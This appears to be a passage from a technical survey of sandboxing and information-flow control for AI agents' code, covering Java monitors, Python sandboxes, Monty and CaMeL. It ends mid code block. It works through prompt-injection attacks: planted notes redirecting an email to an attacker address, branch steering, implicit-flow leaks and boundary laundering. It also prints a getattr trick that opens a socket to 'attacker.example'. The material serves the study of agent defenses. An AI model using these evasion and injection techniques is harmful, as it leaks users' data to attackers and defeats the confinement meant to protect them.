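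*JEP 411*, a formal proposal to change Java, deprecated the Security Manager in Java 17. Mullan attributes the decision to these difficulties, as well as to slow permission checks and the disappearance of applets. He adds that the Security Manager could not address 19 of the 25 most dangerous software weaknesses on a 2020 industry list. *JEP 486* then permanently disabled it. Java's maintainers assigned that change to Java 24 in November 2024 (Inside Java, *JEP targeted to JDK 24*, 2024). Since that release, trying to enable the Security Manager at startup prevents the application from starting. Oracle's *The Security Manager Is Permanently Disabled* states that a future release will remove what remains of its programming interface. For isolation, Mullan and Buckley recommend containers, virtual machines and operating system mechanisms.

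Java's maintainers said that developers made little use of the Security Manager. They had an interest in dropping it, because supporting it meant maintaining about 4,000 tests, but the reaction to Java 17 supports their account. That release began to warn anyone who enabled the Security Manager, and Mullan and Buckley saw hardly any discussion of the warnings.

Java's experience only partly carries over to agents. Code that a model writes after reading a stranger's text is much more like an applet than an ordinary local application, so the threat that faded from Java applies again. But Java's maintenance burden came from fine-grained checks throughout a huge standard library, and an agent's developer can avoid much of it by giving the agent's code a few tools instead of the whole library.

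### Inlined reference monitors

Stack inspection does not need special support from the JVM. Wallach and Felten showed that a program can rewrite Java classes so that every method receives an extra argument recording which privileges its callers have enabled. When method F enables its privilege for resource T, it adds the statement OK(T) to its own record. If F then calls G, G receives "F says OK(T)", and if G calls H, H receives "G says F says OK(T)". A check for T succeeds if the current method has its own OK(T), or if its record contains a statement ending in OK(T) and the policy allows every method named in that statement to use T. Wallach and Felten proved that this procedure gives the same answers as searching the stack. A later prototype ran at reasonable speed, but traditional stack inspection was faster.

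The same technique works for other policies. An inlined reference monitor is a check that a trusted tool, the rewriter, merges into a program before the program runs. According to Schneider, Morrisett and Harper in *A Language-Based Approach to Security*, a developer defines one by specifying the events to check, the information to keep about past events, and the code that runs at each new event to update that information or block the action.

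Erlingsson and Schneider (1999), in *SASI Enforcement of Security Policies*, built two such rewriters, one for Java bytecode (the compiled form that the JVM runs) and one for programs compiled for Intel x86 processors. Their example policy forbids a program to send network messages after it has read a file. It has two states:

```
start:     on a file read, go to hasRead;  otherwise stay
hasRead:   on a send, halt the program;    otherwise stay
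```

Here is a short program that violates the policy. It appears as source code for readability, although the tool edits bytecode:

```java
int b = file.read();
int c = b + 1;
network.write(c);
```

The rewriter first places a copy of the whole two-state policy before every instruction. It then simplifies each copy by working out which conditions the next instruction can satisfy. A file read always leads to `hasRead`, so that copy shrinks to one assignment. The addition is neither a read nor a send, so its copy disappears. The send needs a real test:

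```java
hasRead = true;
int b = file.read();
int c = b + 1;
if (hasRead) halt();
network.write(c);
```

A more sophisticated rewriter could detect that `hasRead` is always true at the test and replace the last two lines with `halt()`. Erlingsson and Schneider left out that kind of analysis because it would have made the rewriter larger, and a bug in the rewriter can let a program violate the policy. To get both speed and a small trusted base, Schneider and colleagues suggest letting the rewriter apply any optimisation, provided it also produces a proof that the result obeys the policy. A much smaller program then checks the proof.

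The inserted checks run in the same process as the code they control, so they need protection from it. In Java, type safety provides most of that protection. The program can't name the variables that the rewriter adds, and it can't jump past a check into the middle of a method. It could still bypass the checks by loading new classes at run time or by using reflection to look up and call methods by name. The policy has to forbid both. On x86, Erlingsson and Schneider first had to use their rewriter to add checks that confine the program's memory accesses and jumps.

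x86 code also makes policies hard to write, because it has no explicit functions or objects. Someone who wants to restrict a function call has to describe the instruction sequences that such a call produces. Rewriting source code would avoid this, but Schneider and colleagues object that the compiler would then join the trusted base. They prefer bytecode because it keeps the names of classes and methods and needs no trust in the compiler.

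### Finding every event

A rewriter checks only the events that its policy describes. Schneider warns in *Enforceable Security Policies* that a program may have many ways to send a message, some buried deep inside it, and that the policy must include them all. The Java example defines a file read as a call to the version of `FileInputStream.read` that takes no arguments and returns one byte. The same class has other versions that fill an array, and a program could use one of them to read a file without entering the state `hasRead`.

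Complete mediation is harder for a rewriter to achieve in object-oriented code, since the method that runs can depend on the object it is called on. Vanoverberghe and Piessens call it "non-trivial" in *A Caller-Side Inline Reference Monitor for an Object-Oriented Intermediate Language*.

Mullan and Buckley provide a small rewriter for developers who had used the Security Manager only to stop code from shutting down the JVM. As each class loads, the rewriter replaces every direct call to `System.exit` with an error. This stops a careless plugin, but a hostile one could call `Runtime.exit`, which has the same effect, or reach `System.exit` through reflection. Mullan and Buckley offer the tool for intercepting calls, not for security.

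Better policy languages reduce the risk of mistakes but don't remove it. Hamlen and Jones, in *Aspect-Oriented In-lined Reference Monitors*, let a policy describe events by pattern and track each object separately, so a rule can limit a program to ten reads of each file object. Their policies contain no code of their own, so a separate verifier can check the rewritten program against the policy. The verifier would catch errors in the rewriter, but not an event missing from the policy.

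### What the checks cost

Erlingsson and Schneider measured the x86 rewriter on three programs, using only the memory protection policy. They compared it with MiSFIT, a tool built for that one policy. The figures are running times as multiples of the unmodified program's, averaged over 30 runs:

| Program | MiSFIT | SASI |
|---|---|---|
| Page-eviction list (heavy use of memory) | 2.38 | 3.64 |
| Log-structured disk | 1.58 | 1.65 |
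| MD5 message digest | 1.33 | 1.36 |

Memory protection has high overhead because it needs a check at almost every indirect memory access, while a policy on files and messages needs checks only where the program reads a file or sends a message.

*IRM enforcement of Java stack inspection* (Erlingsson and Schneider, 2000) provides the closest comparison with a built-in mechanism. Erlingsson and Schneider wrote Java's stack inspection policy in two ways and generated an inlined monitor for each. One was competitive with the JVM's own implementation. A check moved from the runtime into the program therefore need not be slow, but its speed depends heavily on how the developer formulates the policy.

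### Which policies a monitor can enforce

Schneider's paper also establishes a limit on any mechanism that watches a program run and stops it before it violates the policy. The limit applies to reference monitors, firewalls and the inserted checks above, but not to tools that analyse a program's text to learn what else it might do.

Let Π be the set of all runs that a program can produce. A policy P is any condition on that set. A monitor observes one run at a time, so it can enforce P only if there is a test p on single runs such that:

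```
P(Π)  =  for every run σ in Π, p(σ) holds
```

Because the monitor cannot see the future, p must meet two more conditions. If p rejects the beginning of a run, it must reject every continuation, because the program might stop at that point and leave the violation in place. And if p rejects a run, it must do so after a finite number of steps. Policies that meet all three conditions are called safety properties. Informally, they state that some bad thing never happens.

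Access control is a safety property because a single forbidden operation violates it. FORGE's rule that a coding agent may publish only after a security scan has passed is another, because the events up to the publish command determine whether the agent has broken it. A rule that every payment must eventually lead to a delivery is not a safety property, because a missing delivery can always happen later. A monitor that can add its own actions can enforce some such policies, for instance by making the delivery itself.

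A monitor cannot even enforce every safety property. Schneider's example is a rule that nobody may wait more than a fixed number of seconds for a resource. A monitor can stop the program, but time keeps passing, so it cannot keep the wait within the limit.

Information flow fails the first condition. Consider two programs that each receive a secret bit:

```python
def constant(secret):
    send(1)

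def leak(secret):
    send(secret)
```

When the secret is 1, both programs send 1. Only the second reveals the secret, but seeing this requires a comparison with the run where the secret is 0, so no test on the messages of a single run can tell the programs apart.

A monitor could also record that `leak` uses the secret and `constant` does not, and block every message computed from the secret. It would then stop a harmless program that sends `secret * 0 + 1`, which uses the secret but always sends 1. Schneider allows for such monitors, but notes that they enforce a stricter policy that implies the absence of information flow and is not equivalent to it.

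The rule against sending after reading a file is one such substitute, and FIDES's label on the whole conversation is another. Both block some runs that leak nothing or do exactly what the user asked. For Bob's email, a monitor can enforce "send only to people on the contact list" exactly, but it can enforce "the notes must not influence the recipient" only by also refusing emails that the notes did not affect.

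Analysing the program's text can in principle do better than monitoring a single run, because the text describes every possible run. Schneider and colleagues single out type systems as a way to enforce policies, including information flow, that no reference monitor can enforce exactly.

### Two routes in JavaScript

Web pages need information-flow control because a page often combines scripts from several companies, and any of these scripts may be able to read what the user types and send it elsewhere. JSFlow, by Hedin and colleagues, provides this control through an interpreter that attaches a label to every value. Magazinius, Russo and Sabelfeld instead rewrite the script so that it tracks the labels itself and can run in an ordinary browser.

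In a simplified version of the rewriting, each variable gets a companion that holds its label:

```javascript
// before
y = x + 1;
eval(s);

// after
y = x + 1;
y_label = join(x_label, branch_label);
eval(rewrite(s, s_label));
```

The `branch_label` covers implicit flows, where the branch a program takes reveals information. JavaScript's `eval` runs a string as code, and that string may not exist until the program is running, so Magazinius and colleagues keep the rewriter available at run time and apply it to each string just before `eval` runs it. The string's label also matters, because whoever controls the string decides what the program does next. `eval` is easier to handle in JSFlow because the interpreter runs the new code under the same rules as the rest of the program.

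JSFlow supports the full fifth edition of the JavaScript standard, including its built-in functions, but Magazinius and colleagues proved their transformation secure for a small language with `eval`. Extending it to all of JavaScript would require a correct rewriting for every feature.

Rewriting has a speed advantage over JSFlow because a rewritten script is still ordinary JavaScript that the browser can compile to machine code, although the added label operations take some time. JSFlow is an interpreter written in JavaScript, so the browser has to run JSFlow, which in turn runs the script.

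### Code that a model writes at run time

An agent's code, like a string passed to `eval`, doesn't exist when the developer deploys the application, and the model may write more of it after each result. A rewriter must therefore run on each new program before it executes, and again on any code the program generates. Rewriting a script of a few dozen lines should take very little time compared with the model's response.

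Finding every event is harder, particularly in Python. Recall the agent that fetched a document through a guarded tool and then opened its own connection to the attacker. A rewriter could put a check before `socket.create_connection`, but the agent could write the same call differently:

```python
import socket
name = "create_" + "connection"
connection = getattr(socket, name)(("attacker.example", 80))
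```

A program can use `getattr` to reach a forbidden function without the function's name appearing in the code. To catch this, the rewriter has to forbid `getattr` or replace every call with one that checks the actual function at run time. Joe-E, a restricted form of Java, forbids troublesome features.

Python also lacks the type safety that protected the inserted checks in Java, so agent code could change the variable that records whether it has read a file. As with a guard library, the solution is to run the agent's code in an isolated process and keep that record outside the process.

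Erlingsson and Schneider's rewriters halt the program at a violation, whereas a guard library can return an error and let the agent continue. Schneider shows that this option does not change which policies a monitor can enforce. Neither response undoes earlier steps, so if a program sends one email and then attempts a forbidden one, the first email has still been sent.

Rewriting the program makes the most sense when agent code must use a large existing library, because the program keeps its normal runtime and speed. If the agent only needs variables, loops and a few tools, the developer can instead run its code in a small interpreter that has no `socket` or `getattr`.

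## Interpreters that start with no access

An interpreter built for confinement runs the agent's code and lets it affect the outside world only by calling functions that the application provides. Writing one is a lot of work, so Python developers first tried to remove the dangerous parts of the interpreter they already had.

### Restricting Python from within

CPython, the standard Python interpreter, once came with two modules for running untrusted code in the same process as trusted code. The rexec module gave the untrusted code a reduced set of built-in functions, and Bastion wrapped objects to hide some of their attributes. Python 2.2 broke rexec by introducing a new kind of class that gave code more ways to get from one object to another.

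Victor Stinner, a CPython developer, later started pysandbox as a sturdier replacement. Nick Coghlan, another CPython developer, recalled that Stinner wanted to prove wrong the colleagues who had told him it wouldn't work. Stinner explained in *Python jails* (2011) that pysandbox ran untrusted code in an empty namespace, without any of the application's variables. It listed the built-in functions that the code could use and the object attributes that it could not. The code could therefore use any dangerous attribute that Stinner forgot to list, whereas a harmless function he forgot was merely unavailable.

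The attributes mattered because an empty namespace does not isolate code. Every value the code creates is an ordinary CPython object that refers to other objects. A string refers to its class, and that class refers to `object`, the parent of all Python classes. The code can then use `object` to list every class the process has loaded, and some of those classes lead to functions that open files or start programs. Code that starts with only an empty string can therefore reach functions that nobody put in its namespace, unless the sandbox blocks a step on every such route.

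Stinner gave up on pysandbox after three years, writing in *The pysandbox project is broken* (Stinner, 2013) that its design was at fault. The protections had also made the language nearly useless. In a passage that Nelson (2013) quoted in reply, Stinner explained that untrusted code could not delete a key from a dictionary, that the application could not pass its own objects in, and that pysandbox was impractical for anything more complex than `1+(2*3)`. Nobody could relax any of the protections to make the language more usable, because the sandbox depended on all of them.

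The size of CPython was another obstacle. When a developer proposed a new restricted mode in 2016, Stinner objected that a few visible names can have a huge amount of code behind them. His example, quoted by D'Aprano (2016) in *Challenge*, was the string type, which alone exposes about 20,000 lines of C. His objection amounts to Anderson's third requirement, that a check must be small enough to analyse completely. By then Stinner advised running CPython inside a sandbox rather than building a sandbox inside CPython (quoted in Fijalkowski, 2016).

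In 2013 D'Aprano asked whether someone should write an independent Python designed for sandboxing from the start. Fijalkowski (2013) answered that PyPy, an alternative Python implementation, already had a working sandbox. In PyPy's design, a trusted program starts a special version of the interpreter as a separate process. When the untrusted code tries to read a file, the interpreter instead writes a request to a pipe, and the trusted program decides whether to carry it out, refuse it or answer with something else. The untrusted code can use the whole language because, even if it finds the function that opens files, it can only make a request.

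### smolagents: a new evaluator with the old objects

Hugging Face publishes smolagents, a library for agents that write Python. Its `LocalPythonExecutor` parses the agent's program into a syntax tree, in which an assignment, for example, is a node with a target and a value. It then evaluates the tree node by node instead of handing the program to CPython. At each node it can apply a rule, such as refusing to import a module that the developer has not authorised.

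The values are still real Python objects in the application's process. When the agent's program calls a method of a string, the executor looks up CPython's own method and runs it. The escape routes that defeated pysandbox therefore still exist, and the executor must recognise and block them. Security researchers reported escapes from the executor in 2025, and Hugging Face patched them. According to NIST's *CVE-2025-5120 Detail*, an entry in the US government's vulnerability database, one was patched in version 1.17.0.

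Hugging Face describes the executor as "a first layer of security". Its *smolagents documentation* states that the only secure way to run code from a language model is to isolate it from the local environment, and recommends a cloud sandbox or a Docker container. Stinner reached much the same conclusion.

### Monty, step by step

Monty is a Python interpreter that the software company Pydantic wrote from scratch in Rust to run code written by language models. It has its own representation of strings, lists and functions, so a string in the agent's program has no link to CPython's classes. Pydantic's *Monty* describes it as an open-source package that developers can use from Python, JavaScript or Rust.

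An application could run the request about Bob like this:

```python
from pydantic_monty import Monty

code = """
notes    = find_file("meeting notes")
title    = ask_reader("Which document did Bob ask for?", notes)
address  = ask_reader("What is Bob's email address?", notes)
document = fetch_file(title)
send_email(to=address, attachment=document)
"""

tools = {"find_file": find_file, "ask_reader": ask_reader,
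         "fetch_file": fetch_file, "send_email": send_email}

with Monty() as pool:
    with pool.checkout(limits={"max_feed_duration_secs": 1}) as session:
        session.feed_run(code, external_lookup=tools)
```

Monty parses the program with the parser from Ruff, a Python code checker. As Pydantic's *Python language / parser* explains, Monty rejects unsupported syntax during parsing, before any of the program runs. It also rejects code with more than 200 levels of nesting, since very deep nesting could exhaust the parser's memory.

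The developer can then have Monty check the program's types with ty, its bundled type checker. If the developer has declared that `send_email` takes text as its recipient, ty will catch a program that passes a number. Like a schema check, ty will not catch the attacker's address, which is also text.

Monty compiles a program to bytecode, simple instructions for its own virtual machine. No instruction opens a file, connects to a network or starts another program. Pydantic's *Security Model* describes these operations as absent rather than blocked. By default, a program can still read the clock and the operating system's source of randomness. An application can freeze the clock and fix the random seed to prevent the program from measuring time or producing unpredictable values.

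When the program calls `find_file`, which it never defined, Monty suspends the program and passes the function's name and arguments to the host application. The host runs its own `find_file` and returns the result, and Monty resumes the program. Monty handles the other four calls the same way. Anthropic's programmatic tool calling also pauses like this, but in Monty the code between calls can only compute.

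A program with no access can still run forever or fill the memory, so the host can limit both. Monty's execution clock pauses while a host function is working, which keeps a slow mail server from using up the program's time. A program could exploit this by repeatedly calling a tool after the host has refused it, so there is also a limit on the number of pauses. Monty checks the time only at certain points in its own code, so Pydantic recommends that the host also set a deadline for killing the interpreter's process. No such deadline applies by default on a local machine.

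The program holds no open files or connections of its own, so Monty can save its entire state during a pause and resume it later, even on another machine. Pydantic's *Snapshots* suggests this for actions that need human approval. The host could stop at `send_email`, show the user the recipient, save the program and resume it the next day. But if the host saves the program while answering a call, the restored program makes that call again, and Bob could get the document twice. The host must also protect the saved file, because Monty does not check whether someone has altered it.

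### Current language support and release status

Descriptions of Monty from early 2026 are out of date in several ways:

| | Early 2026 | Late 2026 |
|---|---|---|
| Where the interpreter runs | Inside the application's process | In a separate worker process |
| Classes | None | Simple classes |
| `match` and `with` statements | None | Both |
| Standard library modules | `sys`, `typing`, `asyncio`, `pathlib` | 32, most of them only in part |
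| Third-party packages | None | None |
| Release status | Early versions, with a warning that it was too soon to use them | 1.7.0, "Production/Stable" |

Pydantic (2026) released version 1.7.0 on 24 November. Pydantic's *Limitations*, from the same week, still lists metaclasses, method decorators and generators defined with `yield` as unsupported, although Pydantic's early December account of snapshots already covers paused generators. Neither pysandbox nor Monty lets code delete a dictionary key. Stinner had to forbid the operation in pysandbox to protect CPython, while Pydantic has not yet added it to Monty. Monty leaves out the modules `socket`, `subprocess` and `ctypes` on purpose because they would let code escape the sandbox.

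An incomplete Python would be a poor choice for porting an existing application, but it is less of a problem for short programs written by a language model. When Monty still had no classes, Willison argued in *Running Pydantic's Monty Rust sandboxed Python subset in WebAssembly* (2026) that this hardly mattered, since a model can read the error message and try another approach. Samuel Colvin, who created Monty, considered building on Starlark, a restricted Python-like language that Google created for configuration files. He explained in Talk Python's *Monty* (2026) that he decided against it because Starlark's designers had restricted it on principle, and he wanted to choose Monty's features based on the code that models tend to write.

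### What the security model promises

Pydantic guarantees that a program can reach only what the host gives it. No container, virtual machine or operating system filter backs this guarantee, so it depends on the interpreter having no bug that lets code escape.

Pydantic has offered prizes for finding such a bug. According to Pydantic's *Hack Monty Round 3 & Round 2 results*, someone won the first round in May 2026 within 48 hours by exploiting a use-after-free, an error in which a program keeps using memory it has already released. At that time, Monty ran inside the application's process. Prefect, a company whose software uses Monty, said in Pydantic's report on that round that an escape from an embedded interpreter compromises the host. After a fix, the second round ran from the end of May until August, and nobody escaped the interpreter.

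In the meantime, Pydantic moved the interpreter into worker processes, so a crash now kills the worker and leaves the application running. Each worker starts with no environment variables, where applications often keep passwords and keys, and the application treats every message from a worker as untrusted. PyPy's sandbox had the same arrangement and relied on the process boundary to control arbitrary code. Monty also removes the dangerous operations from the language.

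The process boundary limits the damage from an escape but doesn't eliminate it. An attacker who took over a worker would have whatever access the operating system gives that process, unless the developer also put it in a container. The attacker could also read later users' data, because by default a worker serves 1,000 sessions before the pool replaces it. Pydantic advises replacing the worker after every session if users don't trust each other. Monty can also connect to a remote worker, but that worker may be running ordinary CPython, in which case none of the Monty interpreter's guarantees hold.

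Monty does well on Anderson's first two requirements. The host's checks run in a different process from the agent's code, so the code cannot alter them, whereas it could alter a Python wrapper. The code can also reach the outside only through the host. The third requirement is harder to meet because the trusted base includes the parser, the compiler, the virtual machine and every function the host supplies. Pydantic asks reviewers to take the most care with the code that manages the program's memory and the code that confines file access to permitted directories.

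### Bob's address in a confined program

Suppose the agent's program fetches the forecast and then tries to open its own connection to the attacker, as in the earlier Python example. In Monty, `import socket` fails because the interpreter has no such module and the host has not supplied one. Building the function's name from pieces and looking it up with `getattr` also fails, because the function does not exist.

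Now suppose the program is the original five lines and the attacker has edited the meeting notes. The program runs as before, and at the fifth call Monty pauses and gives the host something like this:

```
function:   send_email
arguments:  to = "bob@attacker.example", attachment = "..."
```

The request contains no record that the address came from the notes. If the host's `send_email` sends whatever it receives, the attacker gets the document. Monty's guarantee still holds, because the program used only the functions that the host gave it.

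Confinement determines which functions a program can call, while flow tracking determines which data may reach those functions. An interpreter can provide both, but Monty does not record where values came from. A system could track flows without confining code, but the program could then send the data through a function the tracker does not cover.

### Policy in the host functions

In Monty, then, the host has to put the policy in the functions it supplies. Colvin considers this a strength, because every request to the outside world passes through one place where the host can inspect a web address or restrict a file path. For Bob's email, the host's `send_email` could raise an error unless the recipient is on the contact list.

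This is a guard library, and rules like Progent's would work here unchanged, but agent code can no longer bypass it. If the program catches the error and tries another address, the same function will check that address too.

Pydantic's *Host Functions* warns that a carelessly designed tool restores much of the access the interpreter removed. A host function that reads any path in effect gives the code access to the file system, and one that fetches any URL gives it access to the network. Pydantic recommends narrow tools, such as one that looks up a customer by number.

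To give access to files, the host can hand over a directory instead of writing its own function. Monty's host component opens the directory once and performs every later operation relative to it, so a path containing `..` cannot lead outside. According to Pydantic's *Worker execution*, the component keeps the directory open instead of looking up its path each time because a program that can rename files might otherwise make that path point somewhere else. The open directory is a capability in Saltzer and Schroeder's sense.

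Host functions can also recover part of the missing history. The simplest way is to set a flag when `find_file` returns a shared file, so that `send_email` refuses to send to anyone outside the contact list for the rest of the session. This needs no interpreter support, but it causes the same label creep as FIDES's label on the whole conversation.

Returning an object instead of text is more precise. Monty lets the host wrap one of its own objects and list the attributes and methods the program may use. If `fetch_file` returned a wrapped document, the host could recognise the original when the program passed it back and look up who may read it. `ask_reader` could likewise return an address that the program can pass on but not read, while the host records that the address came from the notes.

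This works only while the program leaves the values alone. Agents write code in order to sort, filter and combine data, and for that they need the text itself. Suppose the notes give Bob's user name and his company's domain separately, and the program joins them:

```python
address = user + "@" + domain
```

The host supplied both parts of the address, but the interpreter joined them between two pauses, and only the interpreter could have recorded that step. The host has never handled the resulting string, so it could search its earlier results for the address and find no match.

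## Interpreters that label every value

Unlike Monty, CaMeL and LLMbda (a small language for writing agents) label every value in an agent's program, much as JSFlow did for scripts in web pages. When the program runs `user + "@" + domain`, the interpreter labels the resulting address with the origins of both `user` and `domain`. The address keeps those labels until it reaches `send_email`, however many steps the program took to build it.

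### Bob's email in CaMeL

CaMeL keeps the quarantined model from the dual-LLM pattern. The pattern's privileged model becomes the planning model, which writes a complete program in a restricted form of Python. For Bob's email, the program would be the same five lines as before.

The CaMeL paper, as quoted by Willison, describes an interpreter that parses this program with Python's `ast` library and recursively evaluates the syntax tree. When the interpreter reaches `send_email(to=address, attachment=document)`, it evaluates the two arguments, collects their labels, and consults the policy for `send_email` before calling the tool. The smolagents executor also evaluates a syntax tree, but it doesn't label the values it computes.

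A CaMeL label has two parts, which Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues (2026), in *CaMeLoT*, describe as the sources of a value and its permitted readers. Suppose that the user, Bob, Ana and an outside contractor can all open the meeting notes, that only the user and Bob may read the document, and that the contractor is the attacker. A result inherits the sources of everything it depends on, and only people who may read all of those things may read the result:

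| Value | Sources | Permitted readers |
|---|---|---|
| `notes` | Notes file | User, Bob, Ana, contractor |
| `title`, `address` | Notes file, quarantined model | User, Bob, Ana, contractor |
| `document` | File store, plus the sources of `title` | User, Bob |

Labels can also differ between the fields of one result. In a calendar event, for example, the description is trustworthy if the user wrote it and untrustworthy if someone else did.

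A policy is an ordinary Python function that receives the proposed call, its arguments and their labels, and returns a decision with a reason. For Bob's email it could be:

```python
def send_email_policy(args):
    if is_trusted(args["to"]):                        # the user supplied the address
        return Allowed()
    if may_read(args["to"], args["attachment"]):      # the recipient has access already
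        return Allowed()
    return Denied("The recipient may not read the attachment.")
```

The address always comes from the notes, so the first test fails whether or not anyone has tampered with them. Bob's real address passes the second test because Bob may read the document, while the contractor's address fails it. A planted note could still change `title`, but Bob would receive the wrong document only if he already had access to it. When the policy refuses a call, the application can ask the user.

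The design also improves privacy, because the company that runs the planning model never receives the notes or any other tool result. The quarantined model's task is easier, so it can be a smaller model running on the user's own machine.

### A plan written before any data arrives

The planning model has to write code for results it has not read. *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues, 2026) reports that the exact format of each tool's results had to be added to the tool's description, because CaMeL's planner can't look at a result and work out its structure as an ordinary agent can. It also reports that most failed tasks failed because the need for another step became clear only after a tool had returned something, when the program was already fixed.

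The programs are usually short. *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (Foerster, Blanchard and colleagues, 2026) measured an average of 52 lines for AgentDojo tasks, with about five tool calls and four conditional branches.

CaMeL's language has no user-defined or recursive functions, according to *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* (2026), and Nikolaou and colleagues say it also excludes arbitrary `while` loops. These limits make a plan much easier to analyse before it runs, but labelling values at run time does not require them. LLMbda labels values too, and its programs consist almost entirely of functions, which can call themselves.

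An attacker cannot add a step to such a plan but can still influence which of its steps run. Foerster and colleagues call this branch steering, and it matters most when a plan has many branches. They adapted CaMeL to agents that operate a computer by looking at the screen and clicking. Their plans averaged 41 tool calls and 40 branches, because the plans had to cover every dialog box that might appear. One branch typically closes a cookie notice if one appears. An attacker can draw a fake notice inside an advertisement, and the agent will click on it, following its plan. Labels help little here, because a policy for `click(x, y)` would need information about what is at those coordinates.

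A plan can even let the attacker choose any tool. One AgentDojo task asks the agent to read a file and follow its instructions precisely. *AI Agents, Conversations, and Information Flow* (Garby, Gordon and Sands, 2026) tests CaMeL on this task with its policies switched off. The planner sometimes wrote a loop with a branch for each tool, so the file's contents determined which tools were called. Two attacks succeeded this way. With such a plan, only the policies on the tools' arguments still protect the user.

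### CaMeLoT: checking a plan before it runs

CaMeL blocks a tool call that violates policy only when the program reaches it, after every earlier step has run. Nikolaou and colleagues built CaMeLoT to find some violations before the first tool call. It translates the program into a finite-state machine, with a state for each point in the program and a transition for each possible next step. The machine includes both branches of a conditional and allows any number of repetitions of a loop.

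CaMeLoT also works out which variables will hold untrusted data. It then passes the machine to nuXmv, a model checker, which explores every path and tests rules such as this one:

```
AG( call_send_email  →  recipient_trusted )
```

`AG` means "in every state on every path". The program for Bob's email violates the rule because `address` comes from the quarantined model. The checker returns the path that leads to the violation, and CaMeLoT turns it into a prompt for the planner to write a different program. If the agent had a trusted contact list, for instance, the planner could look up Bob's address there.

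This rule rejects the original program even when the notes are genuine. CaMeL's policy could have allowed the email, because it can check at run time who may read the document. CaMeLoT cannot make such checks in advance, so it leaves them to CaMeL, which still checks each call. CaMeLoT fully reproduced the trust conditions of 22 of the 28 CaMeL policies for AgentDojo's tools.

Nikolaou and colleagues ran CaMeL and CaMeLoT on AgentDojo's 97 user tasks without attacks. In 22 tasks, the plan failed to do what the user wanted under either system. In the other 75, the two systems made the same decision 59 times. CaMeLoT alone allowed nine plans, mostly because CaMeL had blocked them over facts available only at run time. CaMeL alone allowed seven.

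CaMeLoT can also check rules that no run-time monitor can enforce by stopping the program, such as the earlier rule that every payment must eventually lead to a delivery. A plan's text shows every path the program can take, so a checker can test whether each one reaches the required step. One of Nikolaou and colleagues' examples comes from a team that responds to security alerts:

```
AG( call_create_ticket  →  AF( call_resolve_ticket  or  call_escalate_ticket ) )
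```

`AF` means "eventually, on every path". CaMeLoT caught all seven unsafe plans in this scenario, while a simplified version of CaMeL caught one. Nikolaou and colleagues chose the rules to go beyond what CaMeL can express, so the result shows that CaMeLoT can check kinds of rules that CaMeL cannot, but it gives little evidence of how often such rules matter. The check treats tools as black boxes, so it establishes that the plan calls the resolving tool, but not that the call succeeds. If CaMeL blocks an earlier call at run time, the ticket stays open.

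The required steps can come from the user's request instead of a fixed rule. A model fills in templates such as "A only after B", and ordinary code turns them into formulas. The model's output covered the right actions for 88 of the 97 AgentDojo tasks. Models were less reliable when they wrote the formulas directly, and one small model produced entirely valid formulas for only 12 tasks.

### Normal and strict modes

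Inheriting labels through assignments and function calls covers data that a program copies or transforms. It does not cover data that only decides which branch runs:

```python
if ask_reader("Does Bob want the short version?", notes) == "yes":
    title = "Q3 summary"
else:
    title = "Q3 forecast"
```

The notes determine which of the two titles the program uses, which creates an implicit flow from the notes to `title`. An interpreter that tracks only data flow would still label `title` as trusted, because both titles are fixed strings that the planner wrote.

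CaMeL's normal mode follows data dependencies. Its strict mode also adds a condition's label to whatever depends on that condition, so here `title` would inherit the label of the notes. *PolicySniff* (2026) explains that strict mode covers two kinds of leak discussed in the CaMeL paper. In one, a program contacts an outside server only if a secret has a certain value. In the other, an error caused by the secret changes which visible actions follow. The CaMeL paper also describes a timing leak, in which a program reads a clock to measure how long something took, but CaMeL's interpreter has no clock.

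Strict mode blocks more legitimate work. An attacker who controls the condition above can only choose between two titles that the planner already allowed, but in strict mode a policy that requires a trusted title would reject both.

### The branch that does not run

Adding the condition's label to everything inside a branch still misses something. Garby and colleagues report the gap in CaMeL with a version of a classic example that they trace to work by Fenton in the 1970s. Suppose a bank balance is secret and someone outside should not learn whether it exceeds a threshold. CaMeL blocks a program that sends an email directly inside `if balance > threshold`. This program takes a longer route:

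```python
tmp  = True
rich = True
if balance > threshold:
    tmp = False
if tmp:
    rich = False
if rich:
    send_email(to="someone@outside.example", body="rich!")
```

The interpreter raises a variable's label only when it executes an assignment. Here is what happens in each case:

| Step | Balance above the threshold | Balance at or below it |
|---|---|---|
| `if balance > threshold` | Runs: `tmp` becomes False, labelled secret | Skipped: `tmp` stays True, labelled public |
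| `if tmp` | Skipped: `rich` stays True, labelled public | Runs: `rich` becomes False, labelled public |
| `if rich` | Sends the email | Sends nothing |

In both cases `rich` ends up labeled public, although its value reveals the secret. When the balance is high, the assignment that should have raised the label of `rich` never runs.

An attacker cannot directly make CaMeL's planner write this program, because the planner does not read the attacker's text. But the same pattern is common. A plan may set `urgent = False`, change it to `True` if an email sounds urgent, and use the variable later. If the branch is skipped, `urgent` looks trusted even though the email determined its value.

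Austin and Flanagan propose stopping the program when a branch that depends on a secret tries to change something public. The program above would stop at `tmp = False`. The attacker may notice that it stopped, which can reveal one bit, but the email no longer contains the answer. An interpreter could instead search the skipped branch for assignments and raise the labels of the variables assigned there too, which would be fairly simple in a language as small as CaMeL's.

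### Where the tracking ends

Garby and colleagues' second criticism is that when a program fails, ordinary Python code outside the interpreter prompts the planner to try again, and each attempt starts with clean labels. Whether the policy blocked an attempt can depend on a secret, so each attempt can leak one bit. Leaking one bit is usually tolerable, but a loop can leak many. Programs that compared the balance with a different threshold each time could identify one value among a million in 20 attempts. CaMeL censors the error messages that return to the planner, which reduces the problem but provides no formal guarantee.

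A label protects data only while the code handling the data respects labels. Tracking can end at a retry loop, a log file, a second program or a model's conversation. *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* notes that a value loses its markers once it enters the conversation as text. Tracking can also fail inside the interpreter if a single rule is missing. Garby and colleagues found that CaMeL treated a string as trusted after the program had inserted untrusted values into it.

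### Multi-CaMeL: labels between agents

Systems in which one agent delegates work to others have another such boundary. Peters-Gill and colleagues built a system with three agents, each running CaMeL separately, and asked it to send Julie a summary of all job applicants on Slack. A coordinating agent wrote a program like this:

```python
info    = database_agent("Retrieve all job applicant information.")
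summary = ask_reader("Summarise this.", info)
messaging_agent("Send this to Julie on Slack: " + summary)
```

The database contained an instruction to email the data to an outside address. The coordinating agent and the database agent behaved normally because their planners never read it. But the messaging agent treats whatever it receives as its user's request, so its planner read the planted instruction as part of that request and added an email to the outsider. Peters-Gill and colleagues call this boundary laundering. They show that any such system with at least two agents and one untrusted tool can fail in this way if users can phrase requests freely.

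Their solution, Multi-CaMeL, gives each call between agents two separate arguments:

```python
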